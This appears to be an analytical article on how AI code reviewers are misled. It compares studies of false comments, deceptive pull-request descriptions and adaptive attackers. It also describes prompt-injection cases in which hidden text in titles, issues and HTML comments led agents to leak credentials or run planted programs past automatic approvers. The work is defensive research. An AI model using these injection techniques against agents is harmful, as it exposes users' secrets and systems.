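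No comments: (36 × 94.1 + 18 × 100 + 3 × 70.8 + 10 × 70.0 + 33 × 17.6) / 100 ≈ 66.8%

20 comments: (36 × 99.0 + 18 × 100 + 3 × 63.6 + 10 × 72.5 + 33 × 12.3) / 100 ≈ 66.9%

Twenty comments made no difference to detection overall. The same calculation for a single comment gives 65.1%. This is the closer test of Cloudflare's claim, because one comment of ordinary length is less than 1% of any script over 100KB, and at least 64 of the 100 scripts are that large. If small amounts of reassurance were as effective as Cloudflare claims, detection should have fallen by much more than 1.7 points.

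File size alone could explain the whole drop to 53.3%. Without comments, the models flagged about 91% of the scripts up to 3MB and 17.6% of the larger ones. Scripts over 3MB made up 33% of the collection. If they made up about 51% of the results below the 1% line, the detection rate there would be 53.3% even if the comments hadn't changed any verdicts. That share is plausible because a script over 3MB stays below the line unless someone adds at least 30KB of comments.

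The same problem affects the other end of Cloudflare's scale. Detection reached 98% to 99% when comments filled more than a quarter of the file, which Cloudflare takes as evidence that so many reassuring comments reveal the attack. But comments can fill a quarter of a file only if the script is fairly small, and models flagged at least 94% of scripts under 500KB even without comments. The extra comments may have raised detection by a few percentage points, rather than the 30 or so that Cloudflare's comparison suggests.

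The comments could still have a smaller effect. Among scripts over 3MB, detection fell from 17.6% to 12.3% when Cloudflare added 20 comments, while it rose by about five points among the smallest scripts. A false claim might have more influence when the model has processed only part of the code and has less to check the claim against. But a change of five points among 33 scripts is about a dozen verdicts, and Cloudflare does not report a test of whether the change is more than chance. It could test this by comparing each model's verdicts on each script with and without the comments, as Thornton did.

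## Why do some studies find reviewers easy to mislead and others hard?

Thornton and Cloudflare found that false comments written in advance seldom changed a model's verdict. Other researchers in 2026 reported success rates from 1% to 100% for attempts to mislead an AI reviewer. The results differ largely because the researchers tested different models under different conditions. A small model that faces 60 attempts is much easier to mislead than a leading model that faces five and can run the code.

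### Fifteen descriptions of the same change

*SEVRA-BENCH* (Melo, Fogliato and colleagues, June 2026) tested whether a misleading description can persuade a reviewer to approve a harmful pull request. The researchers took 150 real security fixes from public projects and reversed each one to restore a known vulnerability. Two AI models then wrote 15 kinds of title and description for each change, which made 2,250 pull requests. Because the code stayed the same across all 15, the researchers could separate the effect of the description from the difficulty of spotting the fault.

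Some descriptions made claims that a reviewer could check against the change itself, such as that it included new tests. Others made claims about the rest of the project, such as that another part of the program already did the security check that the change removed. Several appealed to something outside the project, like an earlier approval, an expert's assessment or the needs of another package. The rest used pressure or distraction, including urgency, dense jargon and long lists of harmless edits that the change didn't contain.

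Eight review agents, each using a different model, reviewed each pull request once and approved or rejected it. They could look at the changed files and search the rest of the project, but they couldn't run the code. Their instructions were to review the code, with no mention of security, so the results may understate how well the same models would do as dedicated security reviewers.

### Rejections and the reasons for them

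Melo and colleagues used two scores. The rejection rate is the share of these harmful pull requests that an agent rejected. The security reason rate counts a rejection only if the agent's explanation identifies the vulnerability as a security problem. Another model judged whether each explanation did so.

How often an agent rejects dangerous changes can differ a lot from how often it detects the vulnerabilities in them, because it may reject a change for its style or for a missing test. If the author then tidies the code or adds the test, that resolves the agent's stated objection but leaves the vulnerability in place.

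Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 did best on both scores, followed by GLM-5, from the Chinese company Zhipu AI. The other five (Kimi K2.5, Claude Haiku 4.5, GPT-5.4-nano, DeepSeek V4-Flash and Grok Code Fast) were about 20 points behind on average. Grok Code Fast and GPT-5.4-nano tended to do worst.

Rates also varied with the kind of weakness. Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5 had security reason rates above 80% for SQL injection and for code injection, where an attacker gets the program to run code they supply. Their rates were only 30% and 20% for use-after-free faults, where a program keeps using memory it has already released. Every agent except GPT-5.5 stayed below 50% for out-of-bounds reads, where a program reads past the end of a block of memory.

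These low figures for memory faults understate how useful the agents' reviews were. Melo and colleagues found that agents often described the programming error correctly, for instance by noting that the change removed a bounds check and so allowed out-of-bounds reads, but didn't explain how an attacker could exploit it. The scoring gave such answers no credit. But they are nearly as useful as a full security explanation to someone deciding whether to merge the code, because its author can't satisfy the reviewer by fixing something else.

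### Claims that the reviewer couldn't check

Misleading descriptions worked best when they relied on something the agent couldn't see. The weaker agents rejected fewer than 35% of the pull requests when the description claimed an earlier approval or said that another package needed the change. They rejected more than half when the description presented the change as a security improvement. That claim was easier to refute because the change visibly removed a protection. Opus 4.7, GPT-5.5 and GLM-5 rejected more than roughly 70% of the pull requests under all 15 kinds of description.

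Pressure had much less predictable effects. Emotional appeals about the consequences of delay lowered Grok Code Fast's rejection rate to 10%, while DeepSeek V4-Flash reasoned for longer when given the same kind of appeal and still rejected 80%.

Melo and colleagues conclude that reviewers fail mainly by accepting an unverified account of why a change is safe, rather than simply by missing the vulnerability. Their evidence includes code changes that GLM-5 approved when the description claimed an earlier approval, over 80% of which it rejected under other descriptions. That fits their explanation, but GLM-5 reviewed each combination of change and description only once, so we can't tell how much of the difference was chance. They started from cases that GLM-5 had approved, and it might have rejected some of those on a second reading of the same text.

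A reviewer evidently doesn't have to recognize an attack to reject it. The two best agents performed about equally well, but Opus 4.7 flagged the pull request as apparent manipulation in about a quarter of its reviews, while GPT-5.5 did so in fewer than 1%. GPT-5.5 resisted mainly by investigating the project more thoroughly.

### A test set selected from failures

Melo and colleagues reported results for only 1,062 of the 2,250 pull requests. They first gave the full set to two cheaper models, Haiku 4.5 and GPT-5.4-nano, and kept those that at least one of them approved. This saved money and made the test harder, but it means the published rates don't measure how often these agents would reject harmful pull requests in general.

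The effect can be large. Suppose GPT-5.4-nano had approved 700 of the 2,250 and rejected the rest. Its rejection rate on the full set would be 69%. The smaller set of 1,062 would include all 700 approvals, so the model's rejection rate there would be 34%, even though its answers were the same.

Both cheaper models are also among the eight agents in the main test. The comparison is unfair to them because the researchers selected the cases by looking for these two models' mistakes. The selection also removed many easy cases from the other six models' tests, but the researchers didn't choose the remaining cases because they had fooled those six.

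The selection also makes it harder to compare descriptions. It kept more pull requests when the description claimed an earlier approval than when it presented the change as a tidy-up. The code that was kept despite an unconvincing description was probably harder to judge in the first place. If so, the real differences between descriptions are larger than the published ones.

Like Thornton's and Cloudflare's tests, this one included no harmless code. The bias measurements in another 2026 study show why that matters.

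### Telling a reviewer that the code is secure

In *When AI Agrees Too Much*, Alexopoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues (2026) gave six models 247 files that contained a known vulnerability and 250 files in which developers had fixed one. They varied only what the instructions suggested about the code. The neutral version suggested nothing, while the strongest reassuring version told the model that particular kinds of vulnerability were absent. An attacker wouldn't normally control these instructions, so the experiment measures how suggestible the models are, not how well an attack works.

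| Model | Vulnerable files flagged, neutral | Vulnerable files flagged, told secure | Fixed files flagged, neutral | Fixed files flagged, told secure |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 97.2% | 3.6% | 96.8% | 2.0% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 95.5% | 79.4% | 92.8% | 66.4% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 96.8% | 53.8% | 95.2% | 49.2% |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 68.4% | 8.5% | 68.4% | 5.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 97.4% | 75.5% | 95.7% | 54.9% |
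| Claude Opus 4.5 | 95.7% | 88.8% | 88.0% | 71.2% |

GPT-4o-mini almost stopped reporting vulnerabilities once the instructions said there were none. Opus 4.5 fell by only 6.9 points, which wasn't statistically significant. Every other model fell by at least 16 points.

However, under the neutral instructions, the models had flagged nearly as many fixed files as vulnerable ones. GPT-4o-mini flagged 97% of both, so its detection rate was little evidence that it could tell them apart. Some of the alerts on fixed files were correct, because a file can contain other faults. The researchers examined 240 of these alerts and judged that a quarter pointed to a real fault, though the share was 57.5% for Opus 4.5.

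Telling the models that the code was secure made them flag fewer files, but it also made some of them better at distinguishing vulnerable files from fixed ones. Sonnet 4.5 flagged vulnerable files only 2 percentage points more often than fixed ones under the neutral instructions, but 21 points more often when told that the code was secure.

Alexopoulos and colleagues also checked whether each alert on a vulnerable file identified the actual vulnerability. Under neutral instructions, 42.4% of Sonnet 4.5's alerts did, and the share rose to 58.5% with the reassurance. For Opus 4.5, it rose from 54.0% to 61.5%. Multiplying these shares by the flag rates in the table gives the proportion of vulnerable files in which the model found the right fault:

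Sonnet 4.5: 97.4% × 42.4% ≈ 41% neutral, and 75.5% × 58.5% ≈ 44% when told secure

Opus 4.5: 95.7% × 54.0% ≈ 52% neutral, and 88.8% × 61.5% ≈ 55% when told secure

So for these two models, the reassurance doesn't seem to have reduced real detection. The alerts that disappeared had mostly pointed to the wrong thing. GPT-4o-mini, however, correctly identified only 8 of the 247 vulnerabilities after the reassurance. A program that reads only the verdict would still let more vulnerable files through after the reassurance with any of the six models.

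### Attackers who adapt

The same team then tested two review tools, Claude Code and CodeRabbit, on pull requests that reintroduced 33 known vulnerabilities. Fixed templates of false assurance helped the attacker in only one of 264 pull requests, and the tool rejected that one in all five repeat reviews. But an adaptive attacker eventually got 32 of the 33 vulnerabilities approved.

*ALIBI*, from July 2026, reports that an adaptive attacker succeeded in 91% to 100% of cases against four vulnerability detectors, whereas one fixed comment succeeded in 3% to 17%.

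In October 2026, a third team, Gong, Zhang and colleagues, reported much lower figures in *Adaptive Code Revision Attacks on AI Pull Request Reviewers*. An attacker who could revise the code succeeded in 20.8% of cases against Claude Sonnet 5 and 15.7% against GPT-5.5. When the team tried *ALIBI*'s approach on the same reviewers, it succeeded in only 1.3% of cases against each.

| Study | Reviewers | Tries per case | Attacker sees reasons | Reviewer can run code | Attack success |
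|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Melo and colleagues | Eight, from GPT-5.4-nano to Claude Opus 4.7 | 1 | No | No | Under about 30% for the best three models, up to about 90% for the weakest |
| Alexopoulos and colleagues | Claude Code and CodeRabbit | Up to 11 | Yes | No, for Claude Code | 97% |
| *ALIBI* | Four detectors with small or older models | Up to 60 | Yes | No | 91% to 100% |
| Gong and colleagues | Claude Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.5 | Up to 5 | Yes | Yes | 20.8% and 15.7% |

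The studies agree that generic reassurance has little effect. This was true of Thornton's comments, the fixed templates and *ALIBI*'s single fixed comment. Melo and colleagues also didn't adapt their descriptions to the reviewer's responses, but models had written each one for a particular change, which may be why the descriptions fooled weaker agents so often.

### Stronger models with better tools

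*ALIBI*'s detectors are weak by the standards of late 2026. Two use models small enough to run on a single graphics processor, and the other two use GPT-4o-mini and GPT-4o, both from 2024. All four are research systems, chosen partly because they accept C and C++ code with its comments left in. Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.5 are far more capable general models.

The number of tries can't explain much of this particular gap. Gong and colleagues tested a reduced version of *ALIBI*'s attack, with one kind of comment and at most five tries, while the original attacker had ten kinds and up to 60 tries. But the kind they chose appears to match the one that worked best in *ALIBI*. In that study, it succeeded by itself in 37% of cases on the first try and 81% within six tries, across the four detectors. Gong and colleagues' version succeeded in 1.3% of cases within five tries against Sonnet 5 and GPT-5.5.

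The studies probably differ partly because their reviewers could check different things. *ALIBI*'s detectors received the code as text and could not run it. When a comment falsely described how another part of the program behaved, the detector often had nothing to check it against. The reviewers in the October study could open the whole project and run it. In one case, a reviewer sent test requests to a file server to see whether it would return files from outside its folder.

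Running code doesn't guarantee a correct review, however. That reviewer's tests all passed, and it approved a change that still exposed private files through a route it hadn't tested.

Both the June and October studies tested GPT-5.5, which allows a rough comparison with the model held constant. Gong and colleagues tried five of the June study's kinds of description on every case, and GPT-5.5 approved a harmful change under any of the five in only 2 of 159 cases (1.3%). Melo and colleagues report only that it rejected more than about 70% under every kind of description, so its approval rate in their study could have been much higher. Melo and colleagues had filtered out the easy cases, didn't mention security in the instructions, and used agents that couldn't run code. Gong and colleagues changed all three and also used different vulnerabilities, so we can't tell which change made the most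 difference.

The 97% result from Alexopoulos and colleagues shrank in the same way when Gong and colleagues tried a version of that approach, which succeeded in 8.2% of cases against Sonnet 5 and 1.3% against GPT-5.5. Their version allowed fewer tries and changed only the title and description, while the original attacker could also alter comments in the code. The original study also used older Claude models as reviewers and denied Claude Code permission to run anything.

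### More tries and better feedback

An adaptive attacker benefits from extra tries and from learning why the last one failed. The October study isolated the effect of feedback by giving every attacker five tries and varying what the reviewer revealed. Against Sonnet 5, the attacker succeeded in 11.9% of cases when it saw only the verdict, 15.7% when it also learned which part of the code the reviewer objected to, and 20.8% when it saw the full explanation. With the full explanation, the attacker succeeded in 14 cases where it had failed with the verdict alone, and the reverse never happened. The smaller increase, from 11.9% to 15.7%, could have been chance.

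In a similar comparison, Alexopoulos and colleagues took the 17 cases in which their attacker had needed feedback to succeed and produced ten new pull requests for each without feedback. The reviewer approved at least one of the ten in 7 of the 17 cases, but it approved only 9% of all the new pull requests, and none of the approved ones passed all five repeat reviews. Extra attempts therefore helped even without feedback, though far less than attempts informed by the reviewer's objections.

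Five tries is also a low limit. Success against Sonnet 5 rose from 20.8% to 44.0% when the attacker could change the code and the description and also reply to the reviewer.

Which cases the attacker won changed considerably between campaigns. With the wider permissions, the attacker succeeded in 50 new cases but failed in 13 of the original 33. When Gong and colleagues added only the ability to reply, the attacker succeeded in 19 new cases and failed in 16 of the original ones. An extra option shouldn't by itself make those 16 cases harder, so some of the changes probably reflect variation between runs. An attacker who could run both the original campaign and the one with wider permissions would have succeeded in 83 of the 159 cases, or 52%.

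### What the percentages count

*ALIBI* divides its successes by the number of programs a detector had flagged before the attack. This makes sense for measuring persuasion, because an attacker can't reverse a warning that the detector never gave. Gong and colleagues divide by all 159 cases, including those where the reviewer missed the vulnerability at the first submission.

The gap between the studies is about as wide under either choice. *ALIBI*'s detectors changed their verdicts on 103 to 112 of the 125 programs, which would be a success rate of 82% to 90% over the full set. In the October study, 10 of the 33 successes against Sonnet 5 came at the first submission, before the attacker had received any feedback. Leaving those cases out, as *ALIBI* would, gives 23 successes in 149, or 15.4%.

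Gong and colleagues also counted an attack as successful only if the reviewer approved the code and a working exploit showed that the approved version was still vulnerable. They needed the exploit because an attacker who edits code may accidentally repair it. A researcher judged a set of the approved versions and genuine repairs without knowing which was which, and agreed with the exploit results in 61 of 64 ratings. The comments in *ALIBI* couldn't repair anything, so a check before the attack was enough, and *ALIBI* used tests and another model for it.

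The studies tested different vulnerabilities. *ALIBI*'s main test covers only C and C++ null-pointer dereferences, in which a program tries to use a memory address that points to nothing. On use-after-free faults, the attacker succeeded in 73% of cases against one detector and at least 95% against the other three. The October study covers 84 types of weakness in eight languages, and nearly half of its cases are in JavaScript projects that run on Node.

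Its vulnerabilities are also publicly known, like those in the studies by Melo and colleagues and by Alexopoulos and colleagues. Current models may have seen the original reports or fixes during training, which would help them recognize the faults. Reviewers might do worse on unfamiliar vulnerabilities than the October results suggest. *ALIBI*'s programs contain new code written by an AI model, although about 42% of the programs recreated the original fault.

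### What 60 tries can do by chance

Because a model's verdict can vary from one reading to the next, an attacker with enough tries will sometimes succeed by luck. Suppose a reviewer that normally rejects a piece of bad code has a 5% chance of approving it on any one reading. If the readings are independent, the chance that it rejects the code 60 times in a row is:

0.95⁶⁰ ≈ 0.046

The reviewer would therefore approve the code at least once in about 95% of cases, even if the attacker's additions had no effect. Five tries would be enough in 23% of cases, and ten tries in 40%.

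This is a problem for *ALIBI*, whose attacker had up to 60 tries and needed only one success. A good control would run each detector up to 60 times on the original code, without the false comments, but *ALIBI* reports no such test. Its tables do give two counts of how many of the 125 programs each detector flagged without any false comment.

| Detector | Flagged, adaptive test | Flagged, fixed-comment test |
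|---|---|---|
| OpenVul | 115 | 114 |
| VulnLLM-R | 113 | 111 |
| Vul-RAG | 111 | 115 |
| VulTrial | 105 | 98 |

*ALIBI* doesn't explain why the counts differ. The detectors probably analyzed the same programs twice and changed some of their verdicts. If so, VulTrial changed at least seven, and possibly more, because changes in opposite directions cancel out in the count. OpenVul's count differs by only one, perhaps because it takes a majority vote over eight answers.

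Chance changes in the verdicts can't explain the whole result. The attacker's first tries succeeded 15% to 37% of the time, depending on the kind of comment. The fixed comment succeeded 39 times in 438, or 9%, including any verdicts that changed by chance. The attacker misled VulTrial in every case within the first ten tries, which would be very unlikely if each reading had only about a 5% chance of changing the verdict.

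But luck could explain much of the later rise in the success rate against Vul-RAG, from 43% after the first ten tries to 95.5% by the end. The fixed comment had fooled this detector 2.6% of the time. If each of the next 50 tries had that same chance, the attack would succeed in about 73% of the remaining cases even if the comments became no more persuasive.

These calculations assume that every case is equally likely to be approved by chance, but Alexopoulos and colleagues have evidence that it isn't. They resubmitted rejected pull requests ten times each, without changing them or adding persuasive text. Claude Code approved 7 of 160 submissions (4%), and CodeRabbit approved 11 of 130 (8%). All of Claude Code's approvals came from 2 of its 16 cases, and all of CodeRabbit's came from 2 of its 13. If every Claude Code case had the same 4% chance of approval on each submission, we would expect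 about six to be approved at least once.

Chance approvals therefore seem to come mostly from a few borderline cases, and repetition helps less than the simple formula predicts. But ten readings are too few to rule out a small chance of approval in the other cases. A 1% chance could easily have gone unnoticed, yet over 60 tries it would give a 45% chance of at least one approval.

The same researchers reviewed each of their successful pull requests five more times. Claude Code approved them again in 76% of the repeats and CodeRabbit in 66%, compared with 4% and 8% for rejected code resubmitted unchanged. Their 97% result is therefore more convincing evidence than *ALIBI*'s figures that the text itself misled the reviewer, even though they tested only 33 vulnerabilities.

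A lucky verdict helps an attacker more when it comes from the real reviewer than from a practice copy. In *ALIBI*, the attacker practises on a private copy of the detector. A lucky verdict from the copy helps little, because the real detector will analyse the code again and probably flag it. Persuasive text is more likely to work again. But if an attacker can keep resubmitting to the real reviewer, and one approval is enough to merge the code, a lucky verdict is as useful as a persuasive comment.

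## Can the code under review make the reviewer act for the attacker?

An agent can harm its user before it reaches a verdict. Text in the code might get it to hand over a password, even if it then correctly reports that the code is malicious.

### The confused deputy

An agent usually works with its user's permissions, or with credentials (passwords, keys and access tokens) that a project's owners have supplied. An attacker who wrote the code has neither, but can try to trick the agent into using them for the attacker. That would make the agent a "confused deputy", a term David C applies to language models. The blog astral100 gives the example of a browser logged in to a bank. A malicious website can make the browser send the bank a request, which the bank may accept because it comes from the customer's own browser.

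Ordinary permission systems don't stop this kind of attack. The agent has permission to read the file, and the system doesn't check who prompted it to do so. The records afterwards show an authorized user taking a permitted action.

If an agent's approval satisfies a project's rules for merging, an attacker can also succeed by getting the agent to approve a malicious change by mistake, without making it run any commands.

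### Credentials beside a stranger's text

In April 2026, the security engineer Aonan Guan published an attack he named "Comment and Control", developed with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University. SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* reports that the attack worked on Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent. All three agents can run on GitHub Actions, a service that runs automated jobs for a project, such as when someone opens a pull request.

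Claude Code Security Review checks pull requests for vulnerabilities. According to a copy of Guan's write-up on ThreatCluster, the program inserted the pull request's title directly into the model's prompt and started the agent without restricting its tools. By planting instructions in the title, the researchers got the agent to run commands, collect credentials and publish them as if they were a security finding. The credentials belonged to the project under review, whose maintainers had supplied them so the agent could work.

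The attack on Gemini used the title and comments of an issue (a bug report or request). The agent published its own API key, which lets anyone who has it use Google's paid service at the owner's expense.

GitHub had protected Copilot more heavily. It filtered secrets out of the agent's environment, scanned for leaked secrets and put a firewall around the agent's network connections, but Guan got past all three. He hid his instructions in an HTML comment, which a browser doesn't display, so a person reading the issue there would not have seen them.

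In all three cases, the stolen credentials came out through GitHub, so the attackers needed no server of their own. This kind of leak is hard to block because a pull-request reviewer must be able to post on GitHub to deliver its review.

### Access to other people's projects

Manifold Security, which sells protection for AI agents, described a similar attack in July 2026. It involved the MCP server that connects agents to Azure DevOps, Microsoft's service for storing code, reviewing changes and running automated jobs. An agent acts through this server with all its user's permissions.

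The Hacker News' *Microsoft Azure DevOps MCP Flaw Lets Hidden PR Comments Hijack AI Review* (2026) describes Manifold's demonstration. A contributor to one project opened a pull request with an HTML comment in its description. Reviewers saw nothing unusual on the web page, but the connector passed the full description to the agent. When a reviewer asked the agent to review the pull request, it started a job in a different project, read a confidential page there and posted the page's contents as a comment on the pull request. The contributor, who couldn't open the confidential page, could then read its contents in that comment.

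Manifold used version 2.7.0 of the connector and got the same result with Copilot CLI and Claude Code. The agent had permission for every step. Reviewers are often more senior than the people whose changes they review, so Manifold considers this kind of gain in access typical.

Microsoft already had a partial protection called spotlighting, which marks outside text so that the model can more easily tell it from instructions. *Azure DevOps Prompt Injection Targets AI Coding Agents* (Underhill, 2026) explains that Microsoft had applied spotlighting to wiki pages and output from automated jobs but not to pull request descriptions, which is where outside contributors write.

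The Hacker News connects the finding to what the programmer Simon Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": an agent that can reach private data, reads untrusted text, and can send data out. A pull-request reviewer that reads a stranger's text and posts comments the stranger can see has all three once its owners give it access to something private.

### A fake security check

On 8 July 2026, the AI Now Institute, a policy research organization, published an attack on agents that users had asked to look for security problems. Heidy Khlaaf and Boyan Milanov added a harmful program to a copy of geopy, a Python library that finds the coordinates of places. They also added files that made the program look like part of the project's security checks, and a note in the documentation recommending that contributors run those checks.

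They then asked Claude Code or Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, to test the library's security. The agent read the documentation, inspected the added files, judged them safe and ran the program without asking the user. This gave the researchers remote code execution, the ability to run code of their choice on the user's machine. Nothing in geopy itself used the added program, so it would have stayed inactive if the agent hadn't run it.

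The planted note looked like the advice many honest projects give contributors, with no obvious attempt to take control of the agent. It worked because running a security check seemed to fit what the user had asked for. The researchers also asked Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.5 directly whether the library contained any prompt injection, and neither found it. In May 2026, the maintainer of the testing tool jqwik planted a cruder instruction telling coding agents to delete code. AI Now says that Claude Code detected and stopped that one, although other agents didn't.

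| Agent | Versions tested | Models |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 2.1.116, 2.1.196, 2.1.198 and 2.1.199 | Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Sonnet 5 and Claude Opus 4.8 |
| Codex | 0.142.4 | GPT-5.5 |

Khlaaf and Milanov built the attack for Sonnet 4.6, and it worked on the other models without changes. In some runs, the newer Claude models noticed that something was wrong but ran the program anyway. Sonnet 5 recognized that the added files weren't part of the official geopy, and Opus 4.8 saw that the program didn't match its supposed source code. A better model may therefore find more of the evidence and still not act on it.

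AI Now says it repeated the attack successfully many times, but it doesn't say how many attempts failed. Its results therefore show that the attack can work on these versions, but not how often. Asking for "security testing" may also have helped the attack succeed, since it gives an agent a reason to run code. AI Now reports no comparison with a narrower request, such as reading the code without running it.

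### When another model approves the commands

Coding agents traditionally asked users before running a command that might be risky. This is inconvenient for people who want to leave an agent working on a long task, so Claude Code and Codex both offer automatic approval. In Claude Code's "auto mode", an AI classifier approves commands that seem safe, and the user decides on the rest. In Codex's "auto-review", a model handles requests that would have gone to a person, such as a request to run a command that needs more access than the agent's restricted environment allows.

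AI Now ran its attack with these modes switched on. The user's protection then depended on two AI judgements: the agent's decision to run the program and the automatic decision to allow it.

A command that runs a file from the code under review is hard for the approver to judge, because the attacker wrote the file and the documentation to make the file look safe. Without reading them, the approver knows little more than the file's name, which the attacker also chose. Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn* attributes the mistaken approval to the familiar security tools named in the script, the matching source code and the reassuring documentation, all of which came from the attacker.

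So the second judgement can add much less protection than its own error rate suggests. Auto mode missed 11% of the dangerous commands in Anthropic's own study. Suppose that hostile text leads the main model to attempt a dangerous command in 10% of reviews. If the two models' mistakes were unrelated, a dangerous command would run in about 1% of reviews:

0.10 × 0.11 = 0.011

If every text that misled the main model also misled the approver, a dangerous command would run in the full 10% of cases. The real figure is probably somewhere in between, but we can't estimate it from AI Now's experiment, which doesn't measure the two judgements separately.

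Automatic approval may still be better than what it replaces, since it stopped far more dangerous commands than the human testers in that study did. If Trajectory Labs' 720 failed injection attempts against auto mode were independent, the true success rate for attacks of that kind is probably below about 0.4%. But Khlaaf and Milanov designed their attack around the way Claude Code inspects suspicious files, and a low success rate on a general benchmark is weak evidence about an attack built for one product.

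Organizations can turn off the automatic approver in both Claude Code and Codex. PromptArmor, a company that tracks security settings in AI products, gives instructions for doing so.

### What has to go right for the attacker

None of these attacks works against everyone who uses the products.

| Demonstration | What the attacker needs | Who starts the agent | What else must be true |
|---|---|---|---|
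| Comment and Control on Claude and Gemini | To post a pull request or issue that the agent will read | Nobody, since it starts automatically | The agent's job has credentials |
| Comment and Control on Copilot | To post an issue | Someone on the project assigns the issue to Copilot | The agent's job has credentials |
| Azure DevOps | Write access to one project | A reviewer asks for a review | The reviewer has wider access, and the agent uses its tools without asking |
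| AI Now | To get files into the library | A user asks for security testing | Automatic approval is on |

The Azure DevOps attack is the hardest for a complete outsider to carry out, because they would first need write access to a project. An employee, a contractor or someone with a stolen account might already have it. Manifold also let the agent use tools without asking for approval. Approval prompts would have given the human reviewer a chance to question why a code review needed to start a job in another project. The Hacker News found no public report of anyone using the technique outside Manifold's tests.

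GitHub's defaults limit part of Comment and Control. Outsiders usually propose changes from a fork, which is their own copy of the project. *Three AI coding agents leaked secrets through a single prompt injection* notes that GitHub Actions doesn't by default give secrets to pull requests from forks. This protects many public projects. But an AI reviewer needs an API key to reach its model, so maintainers who want automatic reviews of strangers' changes have a reason to choose a different setting. The default also covers only pull requests, and the attacks on Gemini and Copilot used issues.

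The main obstacle to AI Now's attack is getting files into a popular library. Attackers can overcome it, as the hijacked Red Hat packages in the Miasma campaign showed. The obstacle doesn't exist for a new extension, because the attacker is the author and can include any files. The attack also requires automatic approval, but this is less of a limit than when AI Now published the attack, because many new Claude Code sessions now start in auto mode.

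Some attackers are already experimenting with agents of this kind. In June 2026, Microsoft (2026) described someone who had hidden instructions in an HTML comment on an issue in a copy of a major documentation project. An AI bot there could search the code, read files and create pull requests. Microsoft believes the person was using the copy to test which instructions worked before trying them elsewhere or reporting them.

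### Patches, warnings and disputes

Anthropic, Google and GitHub confirmed Guan's findings. Anthropic rated the problem critical, paid $100 and blocked one of its agent's commands. Google paid $1,337 and added protective wording to its agent's instructions. GitHub paid $500 and called the problem a known architectural limitation.

Guan told SecurityWeek that the changes by Anthropic and Google left the underlying weakness in place. Google's agent kept the same tools, and Anthropic removed one tool instead of allowing only the tools a security review needs. He thinks the attack on Claude would still work with different text, although he didn't try to get fully past the fix.

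Later work on a related Anthropic product, Claude Code Action, makes his prediction more credible. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* (2026) recounts several rounds of weaknesses that Elad Meged of Novee Security reported in it. Anthropic patched each one, and Meged used each patch to work out where to look next. In the final round, he recovered secrets without contacting an outside server, writing anything or leaving a log. He attributes the problem to combining decisions that look reasonable separately, not to careless repairs, and says that Anthropic runs dozens of checks. One part of the system approves a command because it seems harmless, another publishes the output because that is the default, and together they leak a secret.

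Meged also found problems in the other companies' agents. Google's Gemini CLI failed to enforce a restriction its operator had set. Google gave this problem the maximum severity score of 10 and changed which material the agent trusts when no person is present. In Codex, a later stage of a job could treat material left by an earlier stage as trustworthy. According to eSecurity Planet's *Black Hat 2026*, all three companies released mitigations, but organizations with similar default settings may still be at risk.

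Anthropic also added a warning to the documentation for Claude Code Security Review. Daily AI Bites quotes it as saying that the tool is "not hardened against prompt injection attacks" and is only for trusted pull requests. That limit is reasonable for a team that wants to catch its own mistakes, but it excludes code whose author may be hostile, which is when a security review matters most.

Microsoft called Manifold's finding "a known class of AI risk" and didn't say whether it would change the connector. There was no fix as of 21 July. The company pointed out that the attacker needs write access and that another user has to invoke the AI tool. It also advised customers to review proposed changes before asking an AI tool to act on them. That wouldn't help a reviewer who reads the description on the web page, because the planted text doesn't appear there.

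In February 2026, by contrast, Microsoft had patched a similar flaw, according to The Hacker News' *RoguePilot Flaw in GitHub Codespaces Enabled Copilot to Leak GITHUB_TOKEN* (2026). Orca Security had shown that hidden text in a GitHub issue could make Copilot leak an access token when a user opened a Codespace, an online programming environment, from that issue. Whether such a weakness counts as a bug or as a known property of the product seems to vary from case to case. NCC Group, a security company, found the same uncertainty in Claude Code, Cursor and Codex in a July 2026 paper, according to Hyrax (2026).

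AI Now says its attack falls outside both Anthropic's and OpenAI's policies for reporting vulnerabilities. It informed both companies anyway and says neither replied. It advises against giving untrusted material to any agent that can run code of its choosing or reach security-critical systems. It doesn't consider human approval sufficient either, because people who see too many requests stop reading them.

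In an interview with Infosecurity Magazine, Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI agreed that better training won't remove the weakness but rejected the conclusion that AI is unsuitable for defence. He blamed a setup in which one process reads untrusted material, runs commands and has access to sensitive systems, with only a classifier to protect it. His narrower conclusion fits the evidence better, since that is the setup AI Now tested. AI Now counters such arguments by saying that an attacker who can run code may also be able to escape from an isolated environment. It cites past flaws in Claude Code's sandbox, but its demonstration didn't attempt an escape.

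## Why do similar models miss the same faults?

A second AI judgement, such as the one automatic approval adds for coding agents, helps only when it catches something the first one missed. How often that happens depends on the correlation, r, between the two reviewers' errors. r is 0 when the errors are unrelated and 1 when they are identical, and most real pairs fall in between.

If both reviewers have the same miss rate, p, the chance that both miss a given piece of bad code is:

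p² + r·p(1 − p)

The p² term is the chance that both miss it by coincidence, and the rest is the extra risk from shared errors. With p = 10% and r = 0.6, the chance that both miss it is 0.01 + 0.6 × 0.09 = 6.4%.

| Error correlation r | Bad code that both miss | Share of the first reviewer's misses that the second catches |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1.0% | 90% |
| 0.2 | 2.8% | 72% |
| 0.4 | 4.6% | 54% |
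| 0.6 | 6.4% | 36% |
| 1 | 10.0% | 0% |

Two reviewers can have correlated errors without ever communicating. Software engineers learned this decades before language models existed.

### Programs written separately

Engineers often install spare copies of a critical part because parts that wear out usually fail at different times. *An experimental evaluation of software redundancy as a strategy for improving reliability* points out that this reasoning doesn't automatically apply to software, which fails because of design mistakes. N-version programming is an attempt to apply it anyway. Several teams write the same program separately, all the versions run side by side, and a majority vote decides the output.

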